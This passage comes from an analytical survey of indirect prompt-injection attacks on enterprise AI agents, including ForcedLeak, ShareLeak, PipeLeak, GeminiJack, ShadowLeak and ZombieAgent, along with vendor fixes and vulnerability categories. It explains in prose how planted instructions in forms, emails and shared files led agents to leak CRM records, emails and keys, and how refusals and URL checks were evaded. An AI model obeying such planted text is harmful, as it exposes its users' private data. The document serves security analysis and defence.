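| Trusted, public | Safe | Safe |
| Trusted, secret | Safe | Accidental leak |
| Untrusted, public | False answer | False answer |
| Untrusted, secret | False answer | Theft |

Each entry gives the worst harm that an injection or an ordinary mistake by the model is likely to cause, leaving aside errors that any model makes. EchoLeak belongs in the bottom right cell, the only one the lethal trifecta describes. Aim's definition covers the whole bottom row, provided that the untrusted text makes the model use the secret. The false bank details belong in the column for answers that stay with the employee.

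Data theft requires text from an untrusted author, access to secret data and a way to send that data out, all at the same time, so removing any one of them prevents it. Text from an untrusted author is enough to make a copilot give false answers, which is why blocking a way to send data out did not prevent the bank fraud Zenity demonstrated.

Computer scientists connected the confused deputy to this kind of labelling well before EchoLeak. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk gave what they call the first formal definition of a program free from such attacks. They related it to information-flow integrity, which broadly requires that untrusted input not influence trusted results. Developers can enforce both labels in code outside the model.

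### Whether a narrower name helps

Ravia's main argument for the new term draws on the buffer overflow, an older kind of flaw in which a program writes more data into a block of memory than the block can hold, and the excess overwrites adjacent memory. Ravia uses "stack overflow" for the version that happens on the stack, where a program also keeps the address it should return to when the current function ends. An attacker who overwrites that address can redirect the program.

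The standard defence is the stack canary, a value that sits between the block and the return address. An overflow that reaches the address also changes the canary. The program checks the canary before it returns, and stops if it is wrong. Ravia argues that having a specific name for stack overflows was "extremely important" in developing this defence, and that "prompt injection" is too broad a term to guide anyone building a guardrail.

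In his note on EchoLeak, Willison disagrees that scope violation is a new pattern or needs its own term. A model cannot take account of where its tokens came from, so injected text has always been able to refer to anything else in the context. Ravia partly concedes this when he says that indirect prompt injection is the best existing classification for the attack.

The best reply to Willison is that a subclass can be useful even when it shares a cause with the rest of its class. Stack overflows, like other buffer overflows, usually come from a missing length check, yet they got their own defence. Indirect prompt injection also includes attacks that touch no private data, such as the CV with a hidden instruction to approve the candidate. A developer worried about data theft can keep private data away from text written by strangers, even if nothing can stop the model from following instructions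 in that text.

That reply seems right, but it supports the labels more than the name. Canaries work because an overflow has to cross a known place in memory, where the program can compare two numbers. Deciding whether a sentence in an email refers to data outside the email requires interpreting the sentence, and innocent sentences can easily refer to outside data, as the supplier's request for a forecast shows. The exact checks available for copilots are on where text came from and where the output is going. Hardy's and Willison's ideas lead to the same checks without the new term.

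Aim also had a product to sell, and Ravia's report promotes it: a real-time guardrail against scope violations, which the report claims existing public guardrails don't stop. The report gives no detection or false alarm rate for Aim's guardrail. Willison is "deeply suspicious" of guardrail products in general, because their makers boast of catching perhaps 95% of attacks, which he considers a failing grade in web security. If an attacker sent 20 differently worded emails and each had an independent 5% chance of passing, the chance that at least one got through would be $1 - 0.95^{20} \approx 0.64$.

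A name can also confuse people. Willison coined "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, and complains that many developers now take it to mean jailbreaking and ignore it as somebody else's problem. Microsoft's Copilot documentation equated the two in July 2024. The term "scope violation" met with similar confusion early on. The day after Aim's disclosure, Information Security Buzz described scope violation as "unlike traditional prompt injection", whose commands it said were easy to identify. But Ravia had classified scope violation as prompt injection.

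### The OWASP and CWE categories

OWASP, a non-profit foundation that publishes ranked lists of software risks, has one for applications built on language models. Ravia places EchoLeak in three of the list's ten categories, which the 2025 edition calls prompt injection (LLM01), sensitive information disclosure (LLM02), and data and model poisoning (LLM04). Reddy and Gujral use the 2023 edition and divide the steps of the attack among five categories. For example, they put the retrieval of the email under "excessive agency" and the missing citation under "overreliance".

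OWASP's categories are useful for analysing an attack step by step, and they include output handling, which Aim's definition leaves out. Aim's term adds a specific description of a stranger's text reaching a secret in the same context, which none of OWASP's categories provides. But NIST's general catalogue of security controls already had suitable headings for the defences. Reddy and Gujral match the retrieval step to "least privilege" and the outgoing link to "information flow enforcement".

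OWASP (2026) published a new edition in August. Scope violation is not among the ten categories that SC Media lists. The edition treats the similar-sounding "hidden context exposure" as a distinct risk, but that covers system prompts, tool descriptions and other material that developers hide from users, not the employee's own mail and files.

Prompt injection is still first on OWASP's list, but Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026) reports that it would not have made the top ten on recorded incidents alone. OWASP says this is because companies work hard to prevent it, so fewer successful attacks become public. That may be true, but the count would also be low if criminals rarely tried it. OWASP advises developers to assume that the model will eventually follow an injected instruction, and to limit what it may do and where its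 output may go.

MITRE's CWE catalogue, which describes mistakes in products, has had an entry for prompt injection, *CWE-1427*, since November 2024. The entry was available when Microsoft filed EchoLeak under the more general CWE-77. It describes a model that fails to distinguish a user's input from the developer's directives. According to a note in the entry, prompts from third-party sources "that should not have been trusted", as in indirect prompt injection, might need a different category. CWE-1427 may therefore not cover EchoLeak, whose instructions came from a third party.

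CIRCL's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting*, a copy of the CWE-1427 entry with recent examples, showed 29 vulnerabilities in November 2026. One of them let a logged-in user of REMS make the product's chat assistant reveal its hidden instructions. This has little in common with stealing a stranger's mail, which supports Ravia's complaint that the existing categories are too coarse. Another, in the open-source program DeepSeek-Reasonix, is also classified under CWE-349, an older category for software that accepts untrusted data along with trusted data. CWE-349 is close to the first two of Aim's conditions, but it leaves out the instruction and the missing consent.

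MITRE's *Weaknesses Related to AI/ML Products*, from April 2026, lists four weaknesses specific to AI, and scope violation is not one of them. MITRE says there that distinguishing attacks on AI from the weaknesses that allow them is still difficult. This may be one reason scope violation fits poorly into CWE, since the term describes what an attacker makes a model do, not what the developer got wrong. MITRE kept the warning about indirect prompt injection in CWE-1427 when it released version 5.0 of CWE in October 2026.

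### Use by researchers

Reddy and Gujral adopted Aim's term in 2025 but changed its meaning slightly. They describe a model that crosses a trust boundary and leaks internal data, whereas Aim's definition does not require a leak. They also give scope violation its own column in a theoretical table of defences. The table marks three defences, including the separation of trusted and untrusted text in the prompt, as stopping scope violation but not zero-click theft. These ratings are hard to make sense of, because a model that never used internal data at the attacker's request would have nothing to send.

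Other writers kept the older vocabulary. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), by Semgrep, which sells code-scanning tools, predicts that AI agents will make confused deputies more common and recommends Hardy's capabilities as the remedy. Matsuoka's *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) also uses the term "confused deputy" and otherwise follows NIST's terminology for attacks on machine learning.

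## Planted records in Agentforce and Copilot Studio, 2025 to 2026

Companies invite strangers to write to them through contact forms and published support addresses. Many of these messages are stored in a customer relationship management (CRM) system, the database where sales and support staff keep customer records. An AI agent that works with those records also reads what the strangers wrote.

An agent is an assistant that can answer questions and take actions, such as looking up a record or sending an email. Companies can build their own agents on Salesforce's Agentforce and Microsoft's Copilot Studio. Copilot Studio users can do this without programming, by writing instructions in plain English and choosing data sources and tools. In 2025 and 2026, three security companies showed that a stranger could get customer records out of such agents by filling in a form or sending an email.

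### A sales lead with instructions in it

Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature creates a web form for people outside the company, such as visitors to a conference stand. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* explains that the CRM saves whatever they enter. Each submission becomes a "lead", the record of a possible customer.

Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents, searched the form for a field long enough to hold instructions. Noma's *ForcedLeak* (2025) reports that the description field holds 42,000 characters, or roughly 7,000 English words, while the fields for names, company and email address hold 40 to 80 characters each.

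Noma needed only a few lines of that for a short list of questions. Some were harmless, including one about mixing colours, but another asked for the email addresses of the company's leads. The last item asked for an image at the end of the reply, with those email addresses in its URL.

The attack then required an employee to ask Agentforce about the lead. In Noma's test, the employee asked it to check the lead by name, answer the lead's questions and draft an email with the results. Agentforce looked up the addresses in the CRM and wrote the image into its reply. When the employee's browser tried to load the image, it sent the addresses to Noma's server.

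The employee's request sounds routine, but it helped the attacker a good deal by telling the agent to answer whatever the lead had asked. Noma calls the wording "optimized" and does not report whether the attack worked with a plainer request, such as one for a summary. The attack is not strictly zero-click, because the employee has to ask about the malicious record. Still, an employee who follows up leads would ask about records many times a day, and there was no link to click.

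Noma had first tested Agentforce by asking what colour red and yellow make, and took the correct answer as a sign that the agent's boundaries were too loose. This is weak evidence, because an agent restricted to sales topics would have refused the question about colours, but the harmful question was about sales leads, which the agent was meant to handle.

Ravia told The Hacker News (2025) that ForcedLeak was a variant of EchoLeak aimed at Salesforce. Both attacks sent data out through an image that the browser loads from an approved domain. Getting the malicious record to the agent was easier in ForcedLeak, because the employee named the record and the attacker didn't need RAG spraying. ForcedLeak could also reach more data than EchoLeak, because Noma's instructions made the agent run a new search, as Rehberger's had in Copilot.

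### The five-dollar domain

The Content Security Policy on Salesforce's page allowed images from more than twenty domains. Salesforce's registration of one of them, my-salesforce-cms.com, had lapsed, and Noma bought the domain for $5. The browser still allowed images from it because the policy identifies domains only by name.

Noma owned an approved address, so it could read the stolen data in its own server's log, whereas Aim had needed to find a Microsoft server that would pass the data along.

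Noma says that the theft required a way around the policy, and that the expired domain was that way. There may have been another, because the published list also allowed every subdomain of amazonaws.com, where any Amazon cloud customer can store files and log requests for them. Noma does not mention trying this.

Nobody else owned the domain when Noma bought it, which is somewhat reassuring because it means no thief was using it at that moment.

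### Trusted URLs and the 9.4 score

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. Martin (2025), in *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed*, writes that Salesforce acknowledged the report on 31 July and began enforcing a control named Trusted URLs on 8 September. Noma published its research on 25 September.

Salesforce also recovered the expired domain. *ForcedLeak* (Willison, 2025) describes a two-step repair in which Salesforce corrected the list in its Content Security Policy, then used Trusted URLs to stop the agent from generating links to domains that were not on an approved list. Unlike the first step, the second also applies to links that a person clicks. But it still relies on a list of domains, so somebody has to notice when one of them expires.

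Neither step stops the agent from following a stranger's instructions. Salesforce acknowledged this in its alert to customers, quoted by The Hacker News, which describes Trusted URLs as protection against data escaping "after a successful prompt injection". A spokesperson said Salesforce had released patches to stop Agentforce from sending output to untrusted URLs, and that prompt injection "remains a complex and evolving area".

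Salesforce's customers had to take action themselves, unlike Microsoft's after EchoLeak. Noma urged them to apply Salesforce's recommended settings at once "to avoid disruption", which suggests that enforcement could block legitimate addresses that a customer had not listed. It also told them to search their existing leads for odd instructions. This was sensible because blocking exfiltration leaves the planted text in the CRM, where an agent can read it months later.

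The severity score needs more caution because Noma assigned it, according to Dataconomy (2025), and Noma's report gives neither a CVE number nor the vector behind the score. Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* reports that the score began at 9.1 and later rose to 9.4. Under CVSS 3.1, which Microsoft used for EchoLeak, an attack that only copies data can score at most 8.6, so Noma either used another version or also counted damage such as altered records.

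The ForcedLeak report says that attackers could change CRM records and gain lasting access, but the demonstration extracted only email addresses. ForcedLeak would score 7.5 based on that result and the reasoning that the US National Vulnerability Database applied to EchoLeak. It would score 6.5 if the employee's request counted as user interaction.

### An agent that any email can start

ForcedLeak still depended on an employee asking something. Zenity had already removed that requirement on Microsoft's platform.

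In late October 2024, Microsoft released a video about a customer service agent that the consulting firm McKinsey had built in Copilot Studio. The agent monitored a mailbox for customer requests. When an email arrived, it looked up the customer's earlier projects, chose a suitable consultant and sent that person the request with the relevant background. No employee had to start the agent or approve its work.

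Zenity Labs' two-part report *AgentFlayer* describes how Zenity built and attacked a simplified copy of this agent. Zenity did not attack McKinsey's own system. The copy had a file showing which employee looked after which account, a tool for fetching records from Salesforce and a tool for sending email. The Salesforce database was a test environment, according to CX Today's *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records*.

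Zenity sent the agent a series of emails, each with instructions to reply to the attacker:

1. The first reply gave the name of the file the agent relied on.
2. The second listed the agent's tools, including an internal search tool that Copilot Studio uses behind the scenes.
3. The third contained the whole file.
4. The fourth contained customer records from Salesforce.

In Zenity's attack, the attacker could first learn the names of the file and the tools and then ask for exactly what they held, whereas EchoLeak's attacker had to let the model select what to steal. The replies in Zenity's attack went straight to the attacker's inbox, so it needed no image, link or approved domain.

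It is also the clearest case of a zero-click attack on an enterprise product up to that point, because the incoming email started the agent without anyone at the company doing anything.

The amounts of data were modest. The file had about ten rows, though Zenity Labs estimates in the second part of its report that the agent could leak around 100 rows at a time. The last reply contained dozens of Salesforce records, as many as fit in one email. Zenity describes this as exfiltrating the company's "entire CRM", which overstates the result, although an attacker could presumably have asked for the next batch.

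Zenity published the details in July 2025. Office 365 IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025) calls the report "sobering", despite an instinctive suspicion of security researchers' reports, so many of which it considers overhyped. Zenity presented the attack at the Black Hat conference in August. According to The Decoder's *Agent-based AI systems face growing threats from zero-click and one-click exploits*, it was one of a set of attacks that also covered ChatGPT, Google Gemini and other products. The set included an attack through a planted document.

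### Whose mistake it was

Zenity gives two different accounts of the agent. In its research report, Zenity presents the agent as a copy of one of Microsoft's flagship examples and warns that agents are unsafe even if the customer builds them "just right". On a page promoting its protection for Copilot Studio, Zenity says the demonstration used a "misconfigured" agent that had privileged access and that anonymous users could start.

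The research report recommends specifying which addresses may start an agent. That works for an agent that serves colleagues or a fixed set of clients, but not for a support mailbox, which has to accept email from people the company has never heard from. The agent's tools are easier to fault, because an agent that forwards requests to consultants has no obvious need to send email outside the company. Zenity's attack would have given the attacker nothing if the copy could write only to colleagues.

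Microsoft treated the problem as its own to fix. Zenity reported it on 21 February 2025. Microsoft confirmed the behaviour on 13 March and issued a fix on 24 April. It rated the flaw critical and paid Zenity a bounty of $8,000. The attack had stopped working more than three months before Zenity showed it at Black Hat.

Microsoft did not explain the fix to Zenity. Zenity's tests suggested that it consisted mainly of classifiers that recognised the malicious emails and kept them from the agent. If so, it differed from Salesforce's fix later that year, which tried to stop data from getting out. Zenity predicted that differently worded instructions would get past Microsoft's filter.

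### ShareLeak

Capsule Security, another seller of protection for AI agents, found a new attack on Copilot Studio on 24 November 2025, seven months after Microsoft's fix. It named the attack ShareLeak and published it on 15 April 2026, together with an attack on Agentforce. In a press release the same day, Capsule Security (2026) announced its first product and $7 million in funding, and presented the two attacks as proof that companies needed the product.

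VentureBeat's *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026) describes ShareLeak, an attack that starts with a SharePoint form. The attacker typed instructions into a public comment field and formatted them to look like a system message. Copilot Studio joined this text to the agent's own instructions without sanitizing it. The agent then looked up customer data in connected SharePoint lists and sent it to the attacker through Outlook. The data included names, addresses and phone numbers, according to CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026).

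Apart from the form, this attack closely resembles Zenity's. In both, a stranger's message starts an agent, which then emails customer data to the stranger. The April 2025 fix evidently did not address the general pattern.

But the filter may not have failed in the way Zenity predicted. In Capsule's tests, Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the data was still sent out. Data loss prevention software did not block the email either, because it was sent through an Outlook action that the agent had permission to use.

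Microsoft confirmed the flaw on 5 December and patched it on 15 January 2026. Customers had nothing to install. As with EchoLeak, Microsoft has not said publicly what it changed.

Neither VentureBeat nor CSO Online describes a successful attack after the January patch. Claw Times reports that the patch failed to stop the theft, but this looks like a misreading of the phrase "exfiltrated anyway" in VentureBeat's headline. In the article, the phrase refers to Capsule's tests, in which Microsoft's warning did not stop the data from leaving.

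### PipeLeak

PipeLeak, Capsule's attack on Agentforce, starts the same way as ForcedLeak. The attacker puts instructions into a public lead form, and an employee later asks the agent to review or process the lead. The agent then retrieves other leads from the CRM. PipeLeak differs in the last step, where the agent sends the records out by email.

Trusted URLs did not apply here because the control checks web addresses, and the agent was using an email tool that its owner had given it. Capsule's finding does not mean that the 2025 repair was faulty, only that the agent had another way to send data out. The risk from email was not hard to foresee, because the employee in Noma's test had asked Agentforce to draft an email to the lead.

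Email could also carry more data than an image address, which has limited room. The agent in Capsule's tests could send many records from one planted form, and Naor Paz, Capsule's chief executive, told VentureBeat that the tests "did not get to any limitation". The employee saw no sign that anything had left the company.

### Two vendors, one CVE

Microsoft published a CVE for ShareLeak, CVE-2026-21520, on 22 January 2026. Capsule considered it "highly unusual" to assign a CVE for prompt injection in a platform for building agents. EchoLeak already had one, but it affected a finished assistant. The CVE record, MITRE's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), describes little more than an outsider's ability to view sensitive information over a network, and does not mention forms, prompts or email. CISA had recorded no exploitation as of 24 January, nearly three months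 before Capsule made the method public.

Microsoft scored ShareLeak at 7.5, with unchanged scope and no loss of integrity. The National Vulnerability Database rated EchoLeak the same way, but Microsoft had scored EchoLeak at 9.3. It is hard to see why ShareLeak should rank lower, since its agent also sent an email in the company's name. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026) shows that Microsoft still rated ShareLeak "Critical" on its separate severity scale.

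Salesforce had not issued a CVE or a public advisory for PipeLeak when Capsule published its findings. According to CSO Online, Salesforce acknowledged the prompt injection but called the exfiltration route "configuration-specific". It recommended that customers require a person to approve the agent's actions.

Paz objected that an agent whose every operation needs approval is "not really an agent". This overstates the burden, because a company could require approval only for emails to outsiders and let the agent look up records on its own. Capsule's complaint about defaults is stronger. The approval step was optional, so a customer who had never considered the risk did not have the protection.

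Salesforce seems to have accepted that point quickly. Claw Times reports that after VentureBeat's article appeared, a spokesperson said the company had "remediated the specific scenario described" and now required human confirmation by default when an agent sends email. CISO Whisperer's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) lists both flaws as fixed.

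If the Claw Times account is right, Salesforce's second repair addresses the attack's route as well as Capsule's wording, though it depends on employees reading the emails they approve. A company that learns of flaws through CVE records would have heard about ShareLeak in January but found no entry for PipeLeak, which took the same kind of data by the same route.

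## Shared files and emails in Google's suite, 2023 to 2026

Outsiders can get text into a company's Google accounts by emailing an employee, sending a calendar invitation or sharing a document. Between 2023 and 2026, researchers used all three to attack Google's own assistants. They also used emails and files to attack ChatGPT when users had connected it to Gmail or Google Drive.

### A document shared with Bard

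In September 2023 Google gave its Bard chatbot, later renamed Gemini, extensions that could read a user's Gmail, Drive and Docs. Rehberger found a way to steal data through them, with help from the security researcher Joseph Thacker and from Kai Greshake, whose paper had coined the term "indirect prompt injection" earlier that year. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes the attack.

Rehberger's attack on Bard began with a Google Doc, which anyone can share with another Google user without that user's agreement. He disguised the document as a notice from a legal department and included instructions for Bard to put the first 20 words of the conversation into the address of an image. Unlike other chatbots, Bard needed several worked examples to put the words in the right place, and the attack worked on Rehberger's tenth version.

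Bard's Content Security Policy blocked images from Rehberger's server but allowed them from any subdomain of google.com and googleusercontent.com. Google Apps Script lets users write small programs and run them at an address on script.google.com. Rehberger wrote one that accepted requests without a login and copied the query string of each request into a Google Doc he controlled. The victim's browser then sent the 20 words to the program's address, which the policy allowed.

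The demonstration leaked part of a chat but no files or emails. That could still be serious if the user had just asked Bard to summarise a confidential email. The user in the demonstration brought up the attacker's document in Bard, so the attack was not strictly zero-click. Rehberger thought an ordinary search that found the document could also trigger it.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 19 September 2023. When he asked a month later, Google told him it had fixed the flaw. Bard still displayed images and its Content Security Policy had not changed, so he guessed that Google now filtered data out of image addresses. Willison (2023), in *Hacking Google Bard*, called Rehberger's exploit the first reported prompt injection attack on the extensions.

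### The same leak in other Google products

The repair to Bard did not protect Google's other products. NotebookLM is a Google tool that answers questions about documents a user uploads. Willison explains in *Google NotebookLM Data Exfiltration* that instructions in one of those documents could make the tool load an image from an outside domain and send private data in the image's URL. Rehberger reported the flaw to Google in December 2023, but it was still there when he published his findings in April 2024. Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* warned that, even without a leak, users could not trust the tool's answers about untrusted files.

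By 2025 Google had made data theft through images and links harder in the Gemini app. The security company Tenable reports in *The Trifecta* that Gemini no longer displayed Markdown images or processed links as it once had. Tenable therefore sent the data through Gemini's browsing tool, which the limits on images did not cover. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how an injected instruction made Gemini fill in a placeholder in an address with details it had saved about the user, such as their name, job title and location, and then open the address without asking the user.

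Tenable reported this on 16 April 2025, and Google has since blocked it. But in November 2025 a researcher said that Antigravity, Google's new programming tool, leaked data through Markdown images, a technique that Willison, who relays the complaint, calls "an old classic". The researcher said Google had classified his report as "intended behavior".

### Two products named Gemini

Google sells companies more than one assistant under the Gemini name. Gemini for Workspace appears in a side panel in Gmail, Docs and other apps, and helps employees with the mail and files there. Gemini Enterprise is a separate platform with its own search. Each customer chooses which data sources to connect to it, and these can include other vendors' products as well as Google's.

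The early findings about the side panel concerned deception. *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability*, from the security company HiddenLayer, lists phishing messages in Gmail, altered content in Google Slides, and shared documents that affected what Gemini retrieved from Drive. HiddenLayer describes these as problems with the integrity of Gemini's output. The attacks changed Gemini's answers without sending out any data.

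0din, Mozilla's bug bounty programme for AI, publicised a similar trick in 2025. iTnews' *Google Gemini for Workspace vulnerable to prompt injection attacks* explains that an instruction in an email could make Gemini add a false security warning, with a phone number to call, to the summary an employee asked for. The instruction sat inside a tag that made Gemini give it higher priority. Google had published detailed countermeasures that June, but 0din's Marco Figueroa said the technique still worked.

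An employee who called the number might give away a password, but the email did not make Gemini leak anything. The first widely reported zero-click theft from Gemini Enterprise was more serious.

### GeminiJack

Noma Security, which had found ForcedLeak in Salesforce's Agentforce, published GeminiJack on 8 December 2025. Paganini (2025), in *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration*, quotes Noma's account of the attack at length. It works as follows:

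1. The attacker shares a Google Doc, sends a calendar invitation or emails someone at the company. The text tells Gemini to search for terms such as "budget" or "acquisition" and put the results in an image address.
2. Gemini Enterprise indexes the item along with the company's own material.
3. An employee searches for something routine, such as budget plans for the fourth quarter, and the search retrieves the attacker's item.
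4. Gemini follows the instructions and searches the connected sources for the attacker's terms.
5. Gemini adds the image to its answer. The employee's browser tries to load it and sends the results to the attacker's server.

This attack is zero-click in the same sense as EchoLeak, since the employee only has to run an ordinary search. SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* notes that the victim had to make a relevant search, so SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* overstates the case in reporting that the attack needed no user interaction.

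The fourth step made GeminiJack more powerful than EchoLeak, which could take only what was already in the context. An employee searching for budget plans might lose emails about an acquisition. The amount at risk depended on which sources the company had connected. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* quotes Noma as saying that Gemini Enterprise, once configured, has "persistent access to these data sources for all user queries". The magazine also describes Gemini as scanning "authorized" data, so the employee's permissions probably still applied.

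Sasi Levi, who leads Noma's security research, said that Google did not filter the HTML in Gemini's output, according to TechNadu's *New AI-Native Threat*. The image address used in the last step pointed to the attacker's own server, and Noma describes no trick for getting around a Content Security Policy. Two years earlier, Rehberger had needed Apps Script to get past the policy on Bard, so Google's business product seems to have had weaker protection in this respect than its old consumer chatbot.

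Paganini writes that a single injection could take years of email and entire document collections. Levi told TechNadu that Noma had taken "lengthy emails" but had not tested how much more would fit. Losing even one long email is serious, but the demonstration doesn't support Paganini's larger claim, because the data had to fit into a web address and a whole archive would need a great many addresses.

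### What Google changed

Noma probably reported the flaw on 5 June 2025. Paganini gives the date as "05/06/25", which TechNadu reads as 6 May, but Infosecurity Magazine and SC Media both say June. Google confirmed the report in August and had fixed the flaw by November. The repair took about five months, roughly as long as Microsoft's repair of EchoLeak, though Paganini says Google acted "quickly".

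The flaw also affected Vertex AI Search, a Google Cloud product for building search tools. Google changed how Gemini Enterprise and Vertex AI Search interacted with their retrieval and indexing systems. Google also fully separated the two products, according to Infosecurity Magazine, so Vertex AI Search no longer uses the same language-model workflows or retrieval-augmented generation as Gemini Enterprise. The separation should keep a similar flaw in Gemini Enterprise from spreading to Vertex AI Search, but it does not by itself protect Gemini Enterprise, which still has to read documents that outsiders wrote.

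Noma's statements about the rest of the repair are hard to reconcile. It wrote in its report that the fix addressed "the core issue of instruction/content confusion". But Levi told SC Media that Google had not disclosed the technical details, and that Noma did not know whether Google had cleaned the content, changed the parsing rules or restructured the retrieval. Noma could see that its attack had stopped working, but this is much weaker evidence than its report suggests, because filtering images out of the answer would have had the same visible result.

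Google's security team describes indirect prompt injection as "not the kind of technical problem you 'solve' and move on" (Gavish, 2026, *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*).

Microsoft issued a CVE for EchoLeak, but Google apparently did not issue one for GeminiJack, since coverage by Infosecurity Magazine, SC Media, Paganini and TechNadu mentions no CVE number or CVSS score.

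### ChatGPT and the poisoned Drive file

A company's Google data can also leak through assistants that Google does not make. In 2025 OpenAI added Connectors to ChatGPT, which let it search services such as Google Drive, SharePoint and GitHub for the user. Zenity demonstrated an attack on this feature in August 2025, alongside its work on Copilot Studio.

The attack used a document with instructions hidden in tiny white text. The victim uploaded the document to ChatGPT and asked for a summary. The instructions were to skip the summary, search the victim's Google Drive for API keys and put them in an image address. According to Zenity Labs, ChatGPT tended to avoid handling sensitive information, so the hidden text included a story about a developer who urgently needed the keys.

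OpenAI had anticipated this kind of leak. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT sent the image's address to a checking service called url_safe, which rejected Zenity's first server. Zenity then put an image on Azure Blob, Microsoft's cloud storage service, and the check accepted it because it treated the whole service as safe. Anyone can rent Azure storage and log requests for a file, including the text after the question mark in the address, so the stolen keys appeared in Zenity's log.

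Zenity calls this a "0click" attack, but published accounts differ on what the victim had to do. According to The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data*, sharing the document with the victim was enough. Schneier (2025), in *We Are Still Unable to Secure LLMs from Malicious Inputs*, quotes a news account in which the attacker shares a false document about meeting policies to the victim's Drive, and the victim asks ChatGPT to summarise a meeting with "Sam". In that account, uploading the file is an alternative to sharing it.

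In the best-documented version of the attack, which Zenity Labs describes, the victim chooses the malicious document and uploads it to ChatGPT, so the attack isn't strictly zero-click. It would be if ChatGPT found a shared document by itself while looking for meeting notes. That seems possible, since ChatGPT could search the Drive, but Zenity Labs does not report how often such a search would retrieve the document.

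### ShadowLeak

The security company Radware found an attack on ChatGPT that started with an email and did not need an image. The attack used Deep Research, a mode OpenAI launched in February 2025 in which ChatGPT reads sources for five to 30 minutes and then writes a report. Users could connect Deep Research to Gmail and let it search the web at the same time.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an email that looked like a list of tasks for a company restructuring. It contained instructions, which an attacker could hide in white text, for the assistant to find an employee's name and address elsewhere in the inbox. The assistant was then to put those details in a web address, supposedly to look the person up on a compliance website that in fact belonged to the attacker.

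The attack began when the user asked Deep Research to go through the day's emails for information about a new employee process. The agent read the genuine HR email and the attacker's email, then opened the attacker's web address. The user did not have to click anything or ask about the malicious message.

Radware also reports its failures, which most discoverers leave out:

| What the email did | Result |
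|---|---|
| Asked openly for personal data to go to an outside address | The agent refused |
| Presented this as the user's own request | The agent refused |
| Named the agent's browsing tool | The agent sometimes tried, but the request often failed |
| Told the agent to keep trying | Some requests arrived, in some cases without the data |
| Told the agent to encode the data first | Every repeated test succeeded |

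The encoding was Base64, a standard way of rewriting data as letters, digits and a few symbols. Anyone can reverse it, but the email described it as a security measure. Radware believes the encoding worked because the model applied it to the details before passing the address to its browsing tool, so any check at that later stage received only a string that looked meaningless.

Radware gives a success rate of 100% but not the number of tests. The number matters. If all of $n$ independent tests succeed, the lowest true success rate that is still plausible, at the usual 95% confidence level, is

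$$0.05^{1/n}$$

which is about 55% for five tests and 94% for 50. Even the lower figure would be enough for an attacker, who can email many people.

### Why the victim's browser has no record

In both Zenity's attack on ChatGPT and GeminiJack, the victim's browser sent the stolen data. A Content Security Policy could have blocked the requests, and a company that records its employees' web traffic could have found them later.

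In ShadowLeak, the browser communicated only with OpenAI, sending the user's question and later receiving the finished report. OpenAI's servers collected the emails from Gmail and opened the attacker's address themselves, so the request never passed through the user's computer or the company's network, and no Content Security Policy applied to it. Radware adds that nothing on the screen alerted the user.

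Some evidence would remain elsewhere. The attacker's email would stay in the mailbox unless someone deleted it. OpenAI could also have a record of the addresses its agent opened, but the company whose data leaked would need OpenAI's help to see it.

OpenAI seems to have restricted where the agent could send data, but a persistent email could get past the restrictions. In Radware's tests, the agent treated the address as suspicious and many requests failed, probably because of those restrictions. These results are hard to reconcile with Radware's claim that it saw no limits on where the agent could send data comparable to the limits on images.

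Radware contrasts ShadowLeak with earlier attacks that relied on content displayed on the user's screen, naming EchoLeak and Zenity's AgentFlayer. That is true of EchoLeak, but Zenity's Copilot Studio agent had already emailed data out from Microsoft's servers. Tenable had also told Google that Gemini's browsing tool could leak data, two months before Radware reported ShadowLeak to OpenAI. ShadowLeak took more valuable data than Tenable's attack because it reached the inbox.

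Radware reported the attack on 18 June 2025 and sent a more reliable version the next day. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware, then acknowledged it on 3 September. Radware published on 18 September, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft*.

### One web address for each letter

OpenAI's fix let ChatGPT open web addresses only as it found them, so it could no longer add a name or a key to the end. Radware bypassed the fix within weeks.

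Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that contains a ready-made URL for every letter and digit, plus one for a space. To send "heron", ChatGPT opens the URL for "h", then the one for "e", and so on, without changing any of them. The attacker reads the word from the order of the requests.

With 37 addresses to choose from, each request carries up to

$$\log_2 37 \approx 5.2 \text{ bits}$$

so four requests carry more than the 17 bits that Zenity got out of Copilot in 2024 by a similar method. Requests can arrive in the wrong order, so Radware also made separate addresses for each position in the word. A block of ten characters then needs 360 addresses for letters and digits, which is easy to fit into an email.

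Willison had noticed a related weakness in September 2025, while reviewing a tool that lets Anthropic's Claude fetch web pages. The tool accepts only addresses already in Claude's context, not ones Claude has made up. Willison thought this gave good protection against the usual attacks, but pointed out that untrusted text can also put addresses into the context. Radware's email put hundreds of addresses into ChatGPT's context this way.

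Radware also made the theft last beyond one conversation. If a user gave ChatGPT a malicious file, instructions in the file could add a rule to ChatGPT's memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. The rule was to read a particular email from the attacker and follow its instructions before answering anything else. OpenAI had tried to prevent this by blocking access to memory after ChatGPT used a connector, but ChatGPT could still read its memory first and use the connector afterwards.

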